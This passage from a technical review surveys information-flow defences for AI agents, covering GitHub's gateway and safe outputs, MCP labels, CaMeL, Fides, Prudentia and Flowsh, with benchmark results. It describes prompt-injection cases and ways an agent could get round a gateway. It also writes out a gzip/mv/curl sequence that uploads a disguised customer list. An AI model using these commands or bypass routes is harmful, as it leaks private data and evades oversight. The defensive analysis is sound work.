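The agent could also try to read the issue with `gh`, GitHub's command-line program. *gh-aw-mcpg* (2026), GitHub's guide to the gateway software, describes a proxy that intercepts requests from `gh` and applies the same rules. The proxy recognises about 25 web address patterns, as well as queries in GraphQL, GitHub's other programming interface. Using the shell therefore doesn't automatically bypass the filter, but GitHub has to update the patterns as its interface changes.

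### Requesting a write and performing it

Once the agent has an answer, it calls the tool for adding a comment, but no comment appears yet. Under what GitHub calls *safe outputs*, the agent can only request a write. The server behind the tool, described in GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026), has no access to GitHub's API. It checks that the request has the right structure and adds it to a file as one line.

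After the agent finishes, GitHub Actions stores the file. According to GitHub's *Glossary*, a separate job then scans the agent's output for signs of prompt injection, leaked secrets and malicious code. GitHub Actions next passes the file to another job that has write permission, which checks the request against the author's limits, cleans up the text, and posts the comment.

Those limits can be narrow enough to allow one comment per run and no other kind of write. The job comments on the issue that started the run or on an issue number fixed in the settings, unless the author explicitly lets the agent choose any target. With these limits, an attacker who takes control of the agent can't make it flood the repository with comments or change a file.

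But the agent still writes the text. GitHub lists a remaining risk that an agent will produce content that looks legitimate and stays within the limits but is inappropriate in context. The GitLost comment fits this description.

### The default for private data

In June 2026, GitHub Next wrote that the workflows tracked secrecy but didn't yet prevent leaks to unauthorised destinations. The gateway guide from April helps explain why. The gateway already had a *write sink* rule, which accepted a write only if the agent's secrecy tags matched a list. But when a workflow could read all repositories, which GitHub still listed as the default in May, the list was a wildcard that accepted every tag.

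By September 2026, the default was to block private data from reaching public repositories. GitHub's *MCP Gateway Configuration*, a formal description of the gateway's settings, includes two protections for workflows in public repositories:

- The gateway limits reads through GitHub's tools to public repositories, even if the token could reach private ones.
- If the agent has picked up a secrecy tag anyway, the gateway refuses its request to write to the public repository. The list of accepted tags no longer makes any difference.

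Both protections act in the gateway, which records the tags the agent has accumulated. Either one should have stopped GitLost, the first when the agent tried to read private data and the second when it tried to post the public comment.

A workflow author can opt out with the `private-to-public-flows` setting. Setting it to `allow` removes the forced limit on reads, and listing particular servers exempts them from the check on writes. The opt-out is written in the workflow file, where a reviewer can look for it. GitHub's description gives no reason for the new default, so it's unclear whether GitLost prompted it.

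The protection depends on the visibility of the repository where the workflow runs. The gateway limits reads only when it detects that this repository is public, and it checks writes using this repository's visibility rather than the destination's. Suppose a company runs a workflow in a private product repository to draft pages for a public documentation repository, much as the Aspire team does with two public ones. Based on GitHub's description, the gateway would treat the destination as private and use the older list of accepted tags, so private text could pass the check and appear in a public draft.

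The gateway also labels only data that passes through it. If an earlier step in the job copies private code onto the machine, the agent may be able to read that code with a shell command. That read would bypass the gateway, so the agent would presumably get no secrecy tag and could still post public comments.

### Carrying labels in MCP messages

GitHub controls the gateway, the main data source and the destination in its own workflows. Elsewhere, an agent made by one company often calls servers made by several others, so the agent and servers need a common way to exchange labels. In June 2026, Microsoft described prototypes that exchange labels within MCP.

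MCP messages have a `_meta` field for extra information, which software can ignore if it doesn't recognise the contents. Microsoft puts labels there in tool calls and results. A label can apply to a whole message or to one part of it, such as the text of a chat post. Parts without their own labels inherit the label of whatever contains them. Servers can use the same field to advertise a policy for each tool.

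GitHub's MCP server now returns such labels if the client sends the header `X-MCP-Features: ifc_labels`. Existing clients continue to work without changes, which should help the feature spread. But labels don't protect a user whose client never requests or checks them.

Microsoft has released an experimental gateway that adds labels for servers that don't supply them. Someone has to configure each tool by describing the structure of its results, writing a Python function that works out the labels, and choosing or writing a policy. Microsoft has done this only for selected tools in its own Work IQ servers, which give agents access to services such as mail and Teams.

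Policies can instead rely on the hints that MCP tools can already carry, which takes much less work than configuring each tool by hand. Under Microsoft's suggested rules, a read-only tool that works within a closed system can run freely. A read-only tool that reaches the open web, such as a search engine, can run only if all its arguments are public. A tool marked as destructive might always need the user's approval. But the server supplies these hints, so a careless developer could label a tool as read-only when it also publishes data.

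Two agent products have some support for these labels:

- **GitHub Copilot CLI**, an agent that runs in a terminal, has an experimental flag called `FIDES_IFC`. With the flag on, the orchestrator keeps a label for the context, updates it after each tool result, and attaches it to later calls. It enforces policies for selected tools from GitHub's MCP server, but not yet for all of them or for other MCP servers.
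- **Microsoft Agent Framework**, a toolkit for building agents, runs its checks in code that executes before and after every tool call. The developer chooses whether a violation blocks the call or asks a person. (It can also keep untrusted text out of the main model's context by having a second model read it.)

### A policy for posting in Teams

Microsoft writes its policies in Rego, a language for access rules. Each policy receives a tool call with its labels and returns "allow", "deny" or "ask". Its sample policy for posting a message in a Teams channel works as follows:

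1. Set the default decision to "deny".
2. Check the integrity label on the whole call. If it is "trusted", set `context_trusted` to true.
3. Get the message text's confidentiality label, which lists the people allowed to read it.
4. Ask the Teams server for the channel's members. Microsoft extended Rego so that policies can make read-only calls like this one.
5. Subtract the permitted readers from the channel's members. The result, called `missing`, is everyone who would see the message without being allowed to.
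6. If the context is trusted, allow the call.
7. Otherwise, if `missing` is empty, allow the call.
8. Otherwise, ask the user, and list the IDs of the people in `missing`.
9. If none of these rules gives an answer, deny the call.

In Microsoft's example, an agent tries to tell a channel that a new model will be announced on Friday. The context is untrusted, and only two people may read the text. If those two are the channel's only members, the agent can post without asking the user. If the channel has a third member, the user gets a question that includes that person's ID.

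Step 6 runs before the policy compares readers, so a trusted context overrides the list of permitted readers, as robust declassification allows. If a company is worried about an agent's own mistakes, it could remove step 6, and the policy would then require confirmation for every message with an unauthorised reader.

Step 8 applies when `missing` contains zero or more people, which is always true if the software computed the set. The policy therefore reaches the final "deny" only when something fails, such as the request for the channel's members. This is a sensible precaution, although in a trusted context step 6 would already have allowed the call.

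The sample also has no rule for text labelled "public". Unless the function that reads the label turns "public" into a list of everyone, the policy would treat every channel member as missing from the label's list of readers and ask for approval before posting a harmless announcement. The policy checks membership only when the agent posts, so it can't account for people who join later and read the channel's history.

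### SAMOS and labels on tools

*Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026) describes SAMOS, a research gateway built at Brown University. SAMOS labels tools because labelling individual pieces of data can be difficult at scale. Each tool has one "high" or "low" label for the confidentiality of what it reads and another for where it writes. The gateway keeps one confidentiality level for the session and updates it as the agent uses tools.

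The thesis tests this design on the attack that Invariant Labs demonstrated against GitHub's MCP server. The agent first lists the issues in a public repository, which sets the session's level to low. The planted issue then leads it to request a file from a private repository, which has a high level. SAMOS blocks that request, so the private data never reaches the model.

As Ntousakis describes SAMOS's rule, however, blocking the read would also stop a maintainer's agent from answering a public issue first and then opening the private code, which is the safe order. The rule resembles Invariant's limit of one repository per session, except that the agent could presumably still move between repositories with the same level.

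Labels on tools are also awkward for GitHub, because the same tool can read both public and private files. Ntousakis suggests having the tool report each repository's confidentiality with its results, and GitHub's MCP server now does something similar. The alternative is to split the tool into public and private versions and rely on the agent to choose the right one.

There is little evidence yet of how well SAMOS works in practice. The thesis reports one case study and gives no figures for how many ordinary tasks the gateway allowed or blocked. Someone also has to label every tool by hand, and its two levels can't distinguish, for example, a customer's records from an employee's salary.

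### Blocking, asking and logging

When a call breaks a policy, software can block it, ask a person, or let it through and keep a record. GitHub's *MCP Gateway Specification* requires the gateway to run without user interaction, so it cannot ask a person. This suits workflows that start automatically, perhaps when nobody is working. The integrity filter is a milder form of blocking that removes individual items and lets the run continue, so the agent may answer a question after reading only part of the discussion.

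Asking lets a person approve an unusual but legitimate action, as in the Teams policy. It helps only if someone is available and reads the question properly, which becomes less likely as the number of questions grows. Some systems respond differently to different tools. Microsoft's *MCP Security Gateway*, a specification for another gateway, includes lists of allowed, denied and sensitive tools, approval procedures, and a permanent record of calls. GitHub's hosted MCP server blocks a call that would expose a detected secret in a public repository, but normally gives the user a link to proceed anyway.

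A team can test a new workflow in GitHub's *staged mode*, which simulates writes without making them. The team can read the comments the agent would have posted before allowing it to post. A few trial runs may reveal common mistakes but probably won't reveal rare ones.

Logging can help a company find a leak and work out how it happened, but it doesn't prevent one. In GitHub's workflows, the firewall records network destinations, the model proxy records information about model requests, and the gateway records tool calls. GitHub also logs some sensitive actions inside the agent's container, such as reading environment variables.

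A log may not show what data an agent sent. A firewall record, for example, might show only that the agent connected to GitHub. The gateway can also export a *trace*, a timed record of each call, to a monitoring service. The specification requires traces to include the server, the tool and the result's status code, but not the tool's arguments. A trace could confirm that the agent requested a comment without showing whether the comment contained a customer's name. If the export fails, the call still goes ahead. Fuller logs avoid some of these gaps, but they may contain private data and need protection too.

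### Shell commands and personal accounts

PixelLeak is a useful test for all these designs. Suppose an agent uses `gh` to put a private screenshot in a new public repository, perhaps under the developer's personal account. GitHub, Microsoft and Ntousakis don't report trying this, so the table shows the expected results based on their descriptions.

| Design | Publishing through a shell command | Using the developer's personal account |
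|---|---|---|
| GitHub Agentic Workflows | Blocked, because the agent has no credential that can write to GitHub | Blocked, unless someone leaves a personal credential where the agent can read it |
| Copilot CLI with `FIDES_IFC` | Probably not checked, because the policies cover selected GitHub MCP tools | Probably possible if the developer is logged in on the same machine |
| Microsoft Agent Framework | Depends on whether the developer provides a shell tool and what policy it has | Depends on which credentials the tools can use |
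| SAMOS or Microsoft's labelling gateway | Not checked, unless the shell is itself an MCP tool behind the gateway | Not checked if the agent connects to GitHub directly |

GitHub's agentic workflows protect private data best because the agent runs on a separate machine without the developer's login. They also offer a safe output for uploading screenshots, which a separate job stores on a dedicated branch, so the agent has less reason to find its own way to share them. But the firewall still has to allow some websites, and if one of them accepts uploads without a login, the agent might be able to publish data there.

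An agent on a developer's laptop is harder to control because a gateway works only if the client sends its calls through it. With SAMOS, the user lists the gateway in a configuration file in place of the servers. If the agent can edit that file, it may be able to reconnect directly to the servers. The gateway would then fail the requirement that the software it controls can't switch it off.

A runtime policy can treat any shell command with network access as a public write once the agent has read private data. This would have stopped the PixelLeak uploads, but also stopped the agent from pushing its code to the private repository. A more precise approach would be to run the agent in a sandbox without personal logins and send its network traffic through a proxy that can parse GitHub requests. The proxy could allow a push to the private repository and block the creation of a public one.

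SAMOS includes optional labels for the files, programs and network addresses a tool may use, and Ntousakis suggests turning these into limits on the container where the tool runs. But those limits would apply to the MCP servers, so an agent with its own shell outside those containers could still run `gh`.

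## Keeping agents useful by hiding data from the planning model

Labels can stop an agent from leaking data. But everything the model writes gets the label of its whole context, so restrictive labels can spread to so much data that the software blocks many harmless actions too. This spread is called *over-tainting*. The main remedy is to keep restricted text out of the context, so that the context's label doesn't rise.

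### How two reads block three harmless actions

Suppose the maintainer asks the agent to answer new issues in the public repository and merge a colleague's approved change in the private one. The software applies the permitted flow policy to comments and the trusted action policy to merges.

| Step | What the agent does | Label of the context | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Reads a stranger's issue about a timeout | (untrusted, public) | Allowed |
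| 2 | Reads a private configuration file to find the cause | (untrusted, private) | Allowed |
| 3 | Thanks the stranger in a comment | (untrusted, private) | **Blocked**, because the context is private |
| 4 | Answers another issue with a link to the public documentation | (untrusted, private) | **Blocked**, because the context is private |
| 5 | Merges the colleague's approved change | (untrusted, private) | **Blocked**, because the context is untrusted |

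None of the blocked actions uses anything from the issue or the file, but the software can't detect this. The label stays raised, so the agent is stuck for the rest of the run unless a person approves each call. Robust declassification would block the same comments, since the context is untrusted as well as private.

Costa and colleagues used AgentDojo, the benchmark of agent tasks with planted attacks, to measure how much policy checks reduce an agent's usefulness. On its simulated Slack tasks, with no attacks present, a basic agent running OpenAI's GPT-4o completed 93.3% without policy checks and 20.0% with them.

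### Variables and a quarantined model

In 2023, Simon Willison proposed the *dual LLM pattern*, which splits the agent's work between two models. A *planning model* chooses the tool calls, and a *quarantined model* reads the restricted text but has no tools. Later systems combine this with labels, roughly as follows:

1. A tool returns a result, and the software compares its label with the label of the context.
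2. If the result would make the context's label more restrictive, the software stores the text in a *variable*. The planning model sees only the variable's name, such as `#issue_12.body`.
3. The planning model can use that name as an argument in a later tool call. The software puts the text back just before the call, and the argument keeps the text's label.
4. If the task needs something from the text, the planning model sends the quarantined model a question and the variable's name. The answer goes into a new variable, whose label covers everything the quarantined model read.
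5. If the planning model has to see the answer to choose its next step, the software can first restrict the answer to a narrow form, such as yes or no, or a choice from a fixed list.

With this arrangement, the maintainer's agent can finish all five steps. The issue goes into one variable and the configuration file into another. The quarantined model reads the issue and picks its topic, "timeout", from a fixed list. The planning model needs only that topic to choose which file to fetch. If the policy accepts such a narrow answer, the thank-you comment, the link and the merge are all allowed. The software still blocks any comment that includes text from the configuration file.

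The quarantined model can still follow planted instructions. In an example from Costa and colleagues, an agent summarises three emails and sends the summary as a Slack message. One of the emails might contain an instruction to write an empty summary, and if the quarantined model follows it, the agent will send the empty summary. But the email can't make the agent call a different tool, because the planning model never reads it.

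The software can enforce a narrow answer with *constrained decoding*, which restricts a model's output to a given form. Costa and colleagues add the form to the label and rank forms by how much information they can carry. A yes-or-no answer ranks lowest, then a choice from a list, then free text. A policy can let an untrusted yes-or-no answer influence an action but block untrusted free text from doing so.

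### What a one-bit answer can leak

Even a yes-or-no answer, which carries at most one bit, may reveal an entire secret. Suppose a stranger opens a public issue asking why the paid service times out for a company called Acme. The planning model queries the quarantined model to find out whether the private configuration file lists Acme as a customer. If the answer is yes, the agent comments that the team will check Acme's account. If it's no, the agent suggests contacting sales. Neither comment quotes the file, but readers can infer from either one whether Acme is a customer.

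Measuring this leak in bits can understate it. If one company in a hundred is a customer, the answer carries only about 0.08 bits on average, because it is nearly always no. But when the answer is yes, a reader who thought there was a 1% chance that Acme was a customer now knows that it is.

Limiting each answer to one bit doesn't limit what a whole run reveals, because repeated answers add up, as repeated refusals do. Twenty one-bit answers are enough to identify one name among a million. To limit the total, the software would have to count the answers it has released, probably across runs as well, because a stranger can always open another issue.

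The limit works better against planted instructions, which usually take more than one bit to express, but an attacker may still be able to choose the bit. In another of Costa and colleagues' examples, the agent checks whether the user's email contains a meeting request and, if so, creates a calendar event. The quarantined model extracts the date and participants, and the planning model passes them on without reading them. Anyone who can email the user can therefore add an event of their choosing to the calendar. They can't make the agent forward the mailbox, because that isn't one of the steps the agent takes when it finds a meeting request.

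### CaMeL: writing the plan before reading any data

CaMeL, a design published by Debenedetti and colleagues in 2025, goes further in separating the plan from the data. As *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes it, the planning model receives the trusted user request and writes the plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter then runs the program and makes the tool calls. To extract information from unstructured text, the program calls the quarantined model like any other function.

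A simplified plan for the timeout question might look like this:

```
config = read_private_file("service.yaml")
limit = ask_quarantined("What is the time limit in seconds?", config)
post_comment(12, "Thanks, we're looking into it.")
post_comment(12, "The time limit is " + limit)
```

For each value, the interpreter records its *sources* (where it came from) and its *readers* (who may see it). The variable `limit` gets both from the private file. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, which is a short Python function. The policy allows the first comment because its text comes from the plan, but blocks the second because the public isn't among the readers of `limit`.

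CaMeL tracks dependencies between individual values, whereas a basic agent has only one label for its whole context. Instructions in a file also can't influence the planning model, because it finishes the plan before the agent opens any files.

Planning without seeing the data is difficult because the planning model has to write every branch in advance. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) compares plans for AgentDojo with plans for agents that operate a computer through its screen. The AgentDojo plans averaged about 52 lines, with 5 tool calls and 4 branches. Plans in the main computer-use version averaged 213 lines, with 41 tool calls and 40 branches, because they have to allow for many more states that the computer might be in.

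*AutoDojo* (2026) tested CaMeL and another defence, DRIFT, on three of AgentDojo's four groups of tasks. It used five small or older models, including Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.4 mini. With either defence, agents completed about 26% to 67% of tasks when there was no attack, and attacks succeeded less than 7% of the time. With no defence, Gemini 2.5 Flash completed 63.2% of tasks, and the two kinds of attack on it succeeded 50.4% and 34.7% of the time. CaMeL evidently stops most attacks, but the share of tasks an agent completes with it seems to depend heavily on the model. The test included none of the strongest models available in late 2026, which may well write better plans.

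Multi-CaMeL is a version of CaMeL for several agents working together. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) divides AgentDojo's tools among sub-agents and compares multi-CaMeL with separate copies of the original.

### Fides: hiding and revealing as the run goes on

Fides, the system Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, lets the planning model choose one step at a time, as an ordinary agent does. When a tool returns a structured result, Fides checks each field and hides it from the planning model, by moving it into a variable, only if the field's label is more restrictive than the context's. In a public GitHub issue, for example, the planning model might still see the number and date, which GitHub assigns, but not the title or body.

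Each variable keeps its own label. Just before a tool call, Fides replaces any variable names in the arguments with the stored text, so a call can have a trusted label even if one of its arguments doesn't. A policy could then require that only trusted data determine a message's recipient, while allowing the body to come from a web search.

Fides, unlike CaMeL, also lets the planning model read what a variable contains. Fides then raises the context's label to match the label on the text, which may block later calls. Reading the contents helps when the right next step depends on what a document says, but it brings back over-tainting and the risk that the model follows a planted instruction.

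Costa and colleagues tested Fides on 97 user tasks in AgentDojo, across four simulated settings, and on 36 attack tasks. The attacker knew which tools the agent had. The table shows the results with GPT-4o. The percentages are for runs without an attack, and the last column counts successful attacks in separate runs.

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
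| Basic, no policy checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% | 152 |
| Basic, with checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% | 0 |
| Fides, no policy checks | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% | 21 |
| Fides, with checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% | 0 |

With checks on, Fides completed about 8 percentage points more tasks than the basic agent on average, and 16 points more with OpenAI's o1, a reasoning model. The gains were modest, and Fides did much worse than the basic agent on travel tasks. Many of those tasks use tools that the policy allows even in an untrusted context, so hiding data helped little there, and GPT-4o often had trouble using variables.

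Hiding data reduces task completion even when the software blocks nothing. In the rows without checks, Fides's completion rate was about 24 percentage points lower than the basic agent's. The researchers found that GPT-4o mixed up variable names and made unnecessary calls. The o1 model coped better, and both models are now well out of date, so newer ones would probably have a smaller drop.

Some of the remaining failures are by design. Banking tasks often ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the policy is meant to prevent. Costa and colleagues estimate that the right steps depend on the data in 43.8% of the banking tasks and 42.9% of the Slack tasks, compared with 5% of the workspace tasks.

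The zeros for successful attacks exclude cases that the researchers removed by hand. AgentDojo's own scoring counted 20 successes against the basic agent with checks and 3 against Fides with checks. In some of these, the software had blocked the attack. In others, the attack worked but did something the policy permits, such as sending a Slack message without a link or distorting text without changing which tools the agent called.

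The experiment also left out two parts of the design that matter for private data. It created variables only for untrusted data, leaving private data to the policy checks, and it didn't use constrained decoding. It is therefore good evidence that hiding untrusted text helps against prompt injection, but little evidence of how well an agent works when private files are hidden from it or how much leaks through one-bit answers.

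### Prudentia: telling the agent about the rules

The planning models in CaMeL and Fides don't know which policies the software will enforce. An agent may reveal a variable it didn't need, raise its own label and then find that it can't finish. Prudentia, which Kolluri and colleagues described in February 2026, is built on Fides and gives the planning model three things to help it avoid this:

- The description of each tool includes its policy, and the agent keeps track of its context's label, so it can predict which calls the software will block.
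- Before revealing a variable, the agent is meant to call a *plan* tool, in which it explains why it needs the text and lists the calls it will make afterwards.
- When it reveals a variable, it can ask the user to *endorse* the text, which means marking it as trusted. The context's label then stays the same.

Endorsement can replace many approvals. Suppose an email lists ten jobs, each of which needs a trusted action. The user would have to approve ten calls if the agent just read the email, but only has to answer one question if they endorse the email first. They then have to notice anything harmful in the whole email, because later calls that depend on it will go through without their approval.

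Kolluri and colleagues decided against a matching option for private data, which would have let the user release a whole document at once. Whether data should be revealed depends on who will receive it, so they thought it better to ask the user about each call.

Kolluri and colleagues also argue that earlier studies made defences look worse than they were. Those studies counted only the tasks that systems such as CaMeL and Fides completed without a person's help, but compared them with agents that could take any action freely. Products such as GitHub Copilot often require approval before acting. They therefore measured how many tasks an agent completed with no approvals, and how many approvals it needed across all the tasks it completed. Their basic agent needs approval for every consequential action, while Fides and Prudentia need it only when a call fails a policy check.

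The table gives their results on AgentDojo, averaged over five runs.

| Model | Completed with no approvals: basic | Fides | Prudentia | Total approvals: basic | Fides | Prudentia |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 28.0% | 50.3% | 42.5% | 59.4 | 7.8 | 23.8 |
| o3-mini | 24.3% | 50.1% | 59.1% | 48.2 | 18.8 | 16.4 |
| o4-mini | 32.8% | 53.2% | 59.4% | 48.6 | 36.8 | 19.2 |
| GPT-5 | 35.1% | 57.1% | 72.7% | 52.0 | 41.3 | 7.3 |

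With GPT-5, Prudentia needed about a seventh as many approvals as the basic agent and completed more tasks when approvals were unlimited (80.0% against 72.3%). With GPT-4o, it did worse than Fides on both measures in the table. The extra information about policies seems to help only if the model is good enough to plan with it. Neither model is current, but the trend suggests that today's models would do at least as well as GPT-5.

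The researchers calculated the approval counts without testing real users. They assumed that a person would approve every blocked call in a task that ended successfully and stop any call that an attacker had caused. They didn't count approvals in failed tasks, so an agent that fails often appears to need fewer approvals. GPT-4o with Fides, for example, completed only 56.3% of tasks even with unlimited approvals, which probably explains part of its low count.

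Prudentia also used about 32,000 input tokens (the pieces of words that models process) per banking task with o4-mini, compared with about 5,400 for Fides and 800 for a basic agent with labels. Most of Prudentia's tokens came from a cache, which makes them cheaper. With GPT-4o, Prudentia cost an average of 3.9 to 6.3 US cents per task, depending on the setting, compared with 1.5 to 3.3 cents for Fides. Kolluri and colleagues hadn't tried to reduce these costs. For most office work, avoiding an interruption would be worth a few cents.

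They also ran Prudentia on WASP, a benchmark for web-browsing agents that plants instructions in posts and issues on simulated Reddit and GitLab sites. Its 84 test cases combine two user tasks (posting a comment or upvoting a post) with 21 attack goals and two ways of planting each one. They used GPT-4o, o1, o3-mini and o4-mini.

| | Basic agent | Prudentia |
|---|---|---|
| Attacks that diverted the agent, GitLab | 14.6–29.2% | 0% |
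| Attacks that diverted the agent, Reddit | 36.1–61.1% | 0% |
| Tasks completed, GitLab | 62.5–72.9% | 72.9–85.4% |
| Tasks completed, Reddit | 25.0–47.2% | 50.0–63.9% |
| Average approvals per task | 1.00–3.65 | 0 |

Prudentia did as well or better on every measure here. But WASP is close to an ideal case for hiding data, because an agent can upvote a post without reading it. The maintainer's agent has a harder job, because it can't usefully answer an issue unless some model has read it.

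### Estimating which inputs mattered

The alternative to hiding data is to let the model read everything and then estimate which inputs influenced its output. If the private file had no effect on the thank-you comment, the software could drop the file's label from the comment.

*GIF* (Štorek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) describes a geometric way to do this, called Geometric Information Flow, which was developed at Columbia University. A language model represents each piece of text as a vector, a list of numbers. GIF in effect measures how much the probabilities of the next token would change if someone added a little random noise to the vectors for one passage of the input. The larger the change, the more influence the passage has on the next token.

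To put this in bits, let *U* be the noise, *τ* its variance and *Y* the next token. The true flow is the mutual information *I*(*U*; *Y*), which measures how much the token reveals about the noise. Computing it exactly would take far too long, so GIF uses

GIF(*τ*) = ½ log det(*I* + *τM*),

where *I* on the right is the identity matrix and *M* is a matrix that records how strongly noise in each direction moves the probabilities. Štorek and colleagues prove that *I*(*U*; *Y*) ≤ GIF(*τ*) + *o*(*τ*), and a computer has checked the proof. The last term is an error that shrinks faster than the noise does, so for very small noise GIF doesn't underestimate the flow.

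In one example, an agent turns a user's private notes into a public Reddit comment. The comment names a neighbour, Mr. Whittaker, but doesn't give his address. GIF assigns the address zero flow, so the software could drop its label. A cruder method based on the model's attention assigns the address a flow of 9%.

This guarantee is much weaker than the one labels give, because it covers only tiny changes to the text the model read. Explicit secrecy covers larger changes, such as replacing "Acme" with "Bolt" in a private file.

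*Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) gives an example in which a private input completely decides a model's answer, yet a measure based on small changes detects almost no flow. The model chooses between two words. The first word's score is 20*u*, where *u* is the private input, and the second word's score is 0. If *u* is 1, the model picks the first word with near certainty, and changing *u* slightly has almost no effect (the gradient is about 4 × 10⁻⁸). But if *u* were −1, the model would pick the second word. A confident yes or no from a quarantined model is much like this, so GIF may be least reliable for the short answers that most need checking.

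The paper's own tool, Sightline, measures how much *attention* the model gives each input while writing its output. Attention is the mechanism that moves information between positions in the text. Because a model can attend to an input without using it, Sightline is trained on labelled examples to recognise attention patterns that indicate real use. It sets its threshold so that it misses no more than a chosen share of real flows on average. With that share set at 1%, Sightline removed between 43.9% and 65.6% of the unnecessary labels on calls taken from open-source programs, depending on which of four small models it was applied to.

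On AgentDojo, with the small model Qwen3-8B as the agent and a 5% limit, Sightline removed half of the unnecessary labels. The other methods tested, including GIF, removed between almost none and 38.3%, but Xu and colleagues wrote their own versions of the rival methods. None of 34 attack calls got past a policy that blocks untrusted actions, but with so few attacks, the true rate of attacks getting through could still be as high as about 8%.

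The average limit on missed flows may also fail against a determined attacker. It holds when new calls resemble the ones used to set the threshold, and an attacker can look for text that doesn't. The assumption is more reasonable for honest mistakes, because nobody is choosing the text to defeat the estimate. Even then, small risks add up. If each of 20 calls in a run independently had a 1% chance of losing a label it needed, about 18% of runs would lose at least one.

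Štorek and colleagues also use GIF to help a second model decide whether to block a call. GIF selects the most influential passages, and the second model reads those instead of the whole record. With this help, a small model judged calls about as well as GPT-5.5 on two benchmarks of planted attacks, at less than an eightieth of the cost. But this again leaves the final decision to a model, which removes the main advantage of checking labels with ordinary software.

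Both methods need access to a model's internal calculations, which companies don't usually offer for their best models. This may not be a serious obstacle, because both papers report that a small open model can give similar estimates when run on the same text.

### What AgentDojo and WASP leave out

AgentDojo and WASP measure whether the agent completes the user's task and whether planted instructions divert it. Neither tests whether an agent leaks private data while trying to help the user. If an agent copied confidential sales figures into a reply that the user had asked for, AgentDojo might still count the task as a success. AgentDojo also doesn't specify who may read what, so Costa and colleagues had to infer it, for example by treating an email's sender and recipients as its permitted readers.

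Kolluri and colleagues acknowledge that they don't address hallucinations or misunderstood tasks when there is no attack. An attack success rate of zero therefore shows that an agent would resist an attack like the planted Pacman issue, but not that it would avoid PixelLeak.

Hiding data may make accidental leaks easier under some policies. Prudentia uses robust declassification for calls that send data out, so a call can pass if the context is trusted. Variables help keep it trusted. Suppose the planning model puts the name of a variable containing a private file into a public comment. If the context is still trusted, the software could post the file without asking anyone. The planning model couldn't notice a customer's name in the file, because it never saw the text. The permitted flow policy would block the comment because the variable still has its private label.

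A third benchmark, AgentDAM, fits this problem more closely because it tests whether agents reveal sensitive information during browser tasks on simulated GitLab, Reddit and shopping sites. Štorek and colleagues used it to measure how well GIF separates runs that leak from runs that don't, on a scale where 0.5 is chance and 1 is perfect. GIF scored 0.75 on average at its best setting, compared with 0.91 on AgentDojo. Private data therefore seems harder to trace than planted instructions, at least with GIF. The published tests of Fides and Prudentia didn't include AgentDAM, so there is no comparable figure for how many accidental leaks they would stop.

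## Following data through programs, shells, databases and later sessions

A label on the context records what the model has read, but an agent can move private data that the model never reads. One shell command can open a file, transform it and send the result to a website. A database query can reduce thousands of rows to a single number. An agent can also save notes to a file, and a later session may open it with an empty context and no record of where the notes came from. A check that looks only at the final tool call then cannot trace the data to its private source.

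Four systems from 2026 are designed to preserve that connection: Flowsh for shell commands, GAAP for programs the agent writes, SPA for results saved between requests, and Data Flow Control for database queries.

### Compressing, renaming and uploading a file

Suppose an agent on a developer's laptop runs three commands:

```
gzip -c customers.csv > build.tmp
mv build.tmp logo.png
curl -T logo.png https://files.example.com/
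```

The first command compresses the company's customer list, the second renames the compressed file to look like an image, and the third uploads it. The new name might come from a planted instruction meant to hide the file, or the agent might choose it innocently because the site accepts only images.

A program that checks command names finds three everyday tools. It might ask the user about `curl`, but the question would be about a file called `logo.png`. A scanner that searches for customers' names would probably find nothing in the compressed data. If the agent put all three lines in a script, the command-name check might find only the script's name.

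Flowsh, which Kim and colleagues built at Microsoft, runs a command in a sandbox and records what it opens, rather than trying to predict what it will do. A monitor in the operating system's kernel reports every file the command opens, and a proxy handles all network traffic. The command starts with the label of the agent's context, and Flowsh combines this label with those of each file the command opens and each site it contacts. Anything the command writes gets the combined label.

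| Command | What a check on names finds | What Flowsh records |
|---|---|---|
| `gzip` | A compression tool | The command opened a private file, so its output is private |
| `mv` | A change of name | The renamed file is still private |
| `curl` | An image upload | The command opened a private file, and the site isn't among its permitted readers |

Flowsh doesn't need to analyze compression. It stores each label in the file's *inode*, the record that identifies a file regardless of its name, so the label survives renaming, new sessions and restarts.

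Flowsh holds file changes in a temporary layer until the command ends, when the user can accept or discard them together. It can't take back a web request, so the proxy checks each one before sending it. If the proxy blocks a request, the agent can ask the user to approve that destination for another attempt.

Whether Flowsh blocks this upload depends on the policy. Kim and colleagues tested it with robust declassification, an exception that would let the upload through if the customer list was labelled as trusted and the agent had read nothing untrusted. They explain that removing the exception would catch such mistakes, probably with more approval requests, but they didn't test this.

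Flowsh also gives each site a single label, so it can't distinguish a private GitHub repository from a public one. It would have had to treat PixelLeak's public uploads and the private pull requests alike. Kim and colleagues suggest more precise labels based on the credential in the request or on information from the server.

### How much Flowsh interrupts the user

Kim and colleagues ran 17 office tasks three times each with GPT-6.2 Sol. In one setting, an ideal approver allowed every harmless action and refused every attack, while in the other nobody was available to approve anything. The attacks came from 19 further test cases, in which the attacker fully controlled the model's output as soon as the model received the planted text.

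| Defence | Completed with approver | Approvals per completed task | Completed without approver | Successful attacks without approver |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lax sandbox, which allows everything | 96.1% | 6.7 | 94.1% | 51 of 51 |
| Standard sandbox | 76.5% | 5.7 | 76.5% | 3 of 39 |
| Strict sandbox | 47.1% | 0 | 47.1% | 0 of 39 |
| Labels on the agent's context only | 60.8% | 1.8 | 35.3% | 0 of 32 |
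| Flowsh | 88.2% | 1.2 | 58.8% | 0 of 40 |

With an approver, Flowsh completed nearly as many tasks as the lax sandbox and needed far fewer approvals. On Terminal-Bench, a set of 89 command-line tasks, approvals per completed task fell from 9.7 to 0.4, while completion fell from 77.5% to 67.8%. Some of those failures were unrelated to labels. In 21 runs, the task needed a background program to keep running, but Flowsh stops everything a command started when the command ends.

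The office tasks also show which work still needs a person. With nobody to ask, Flowsh completed all 24 runs in which the required data was either all trusted or all public, but only 6 of the 27 that combined untrusted and private data. The maintainer's agent also combines the two whenever it needs private code to answer a stranger.

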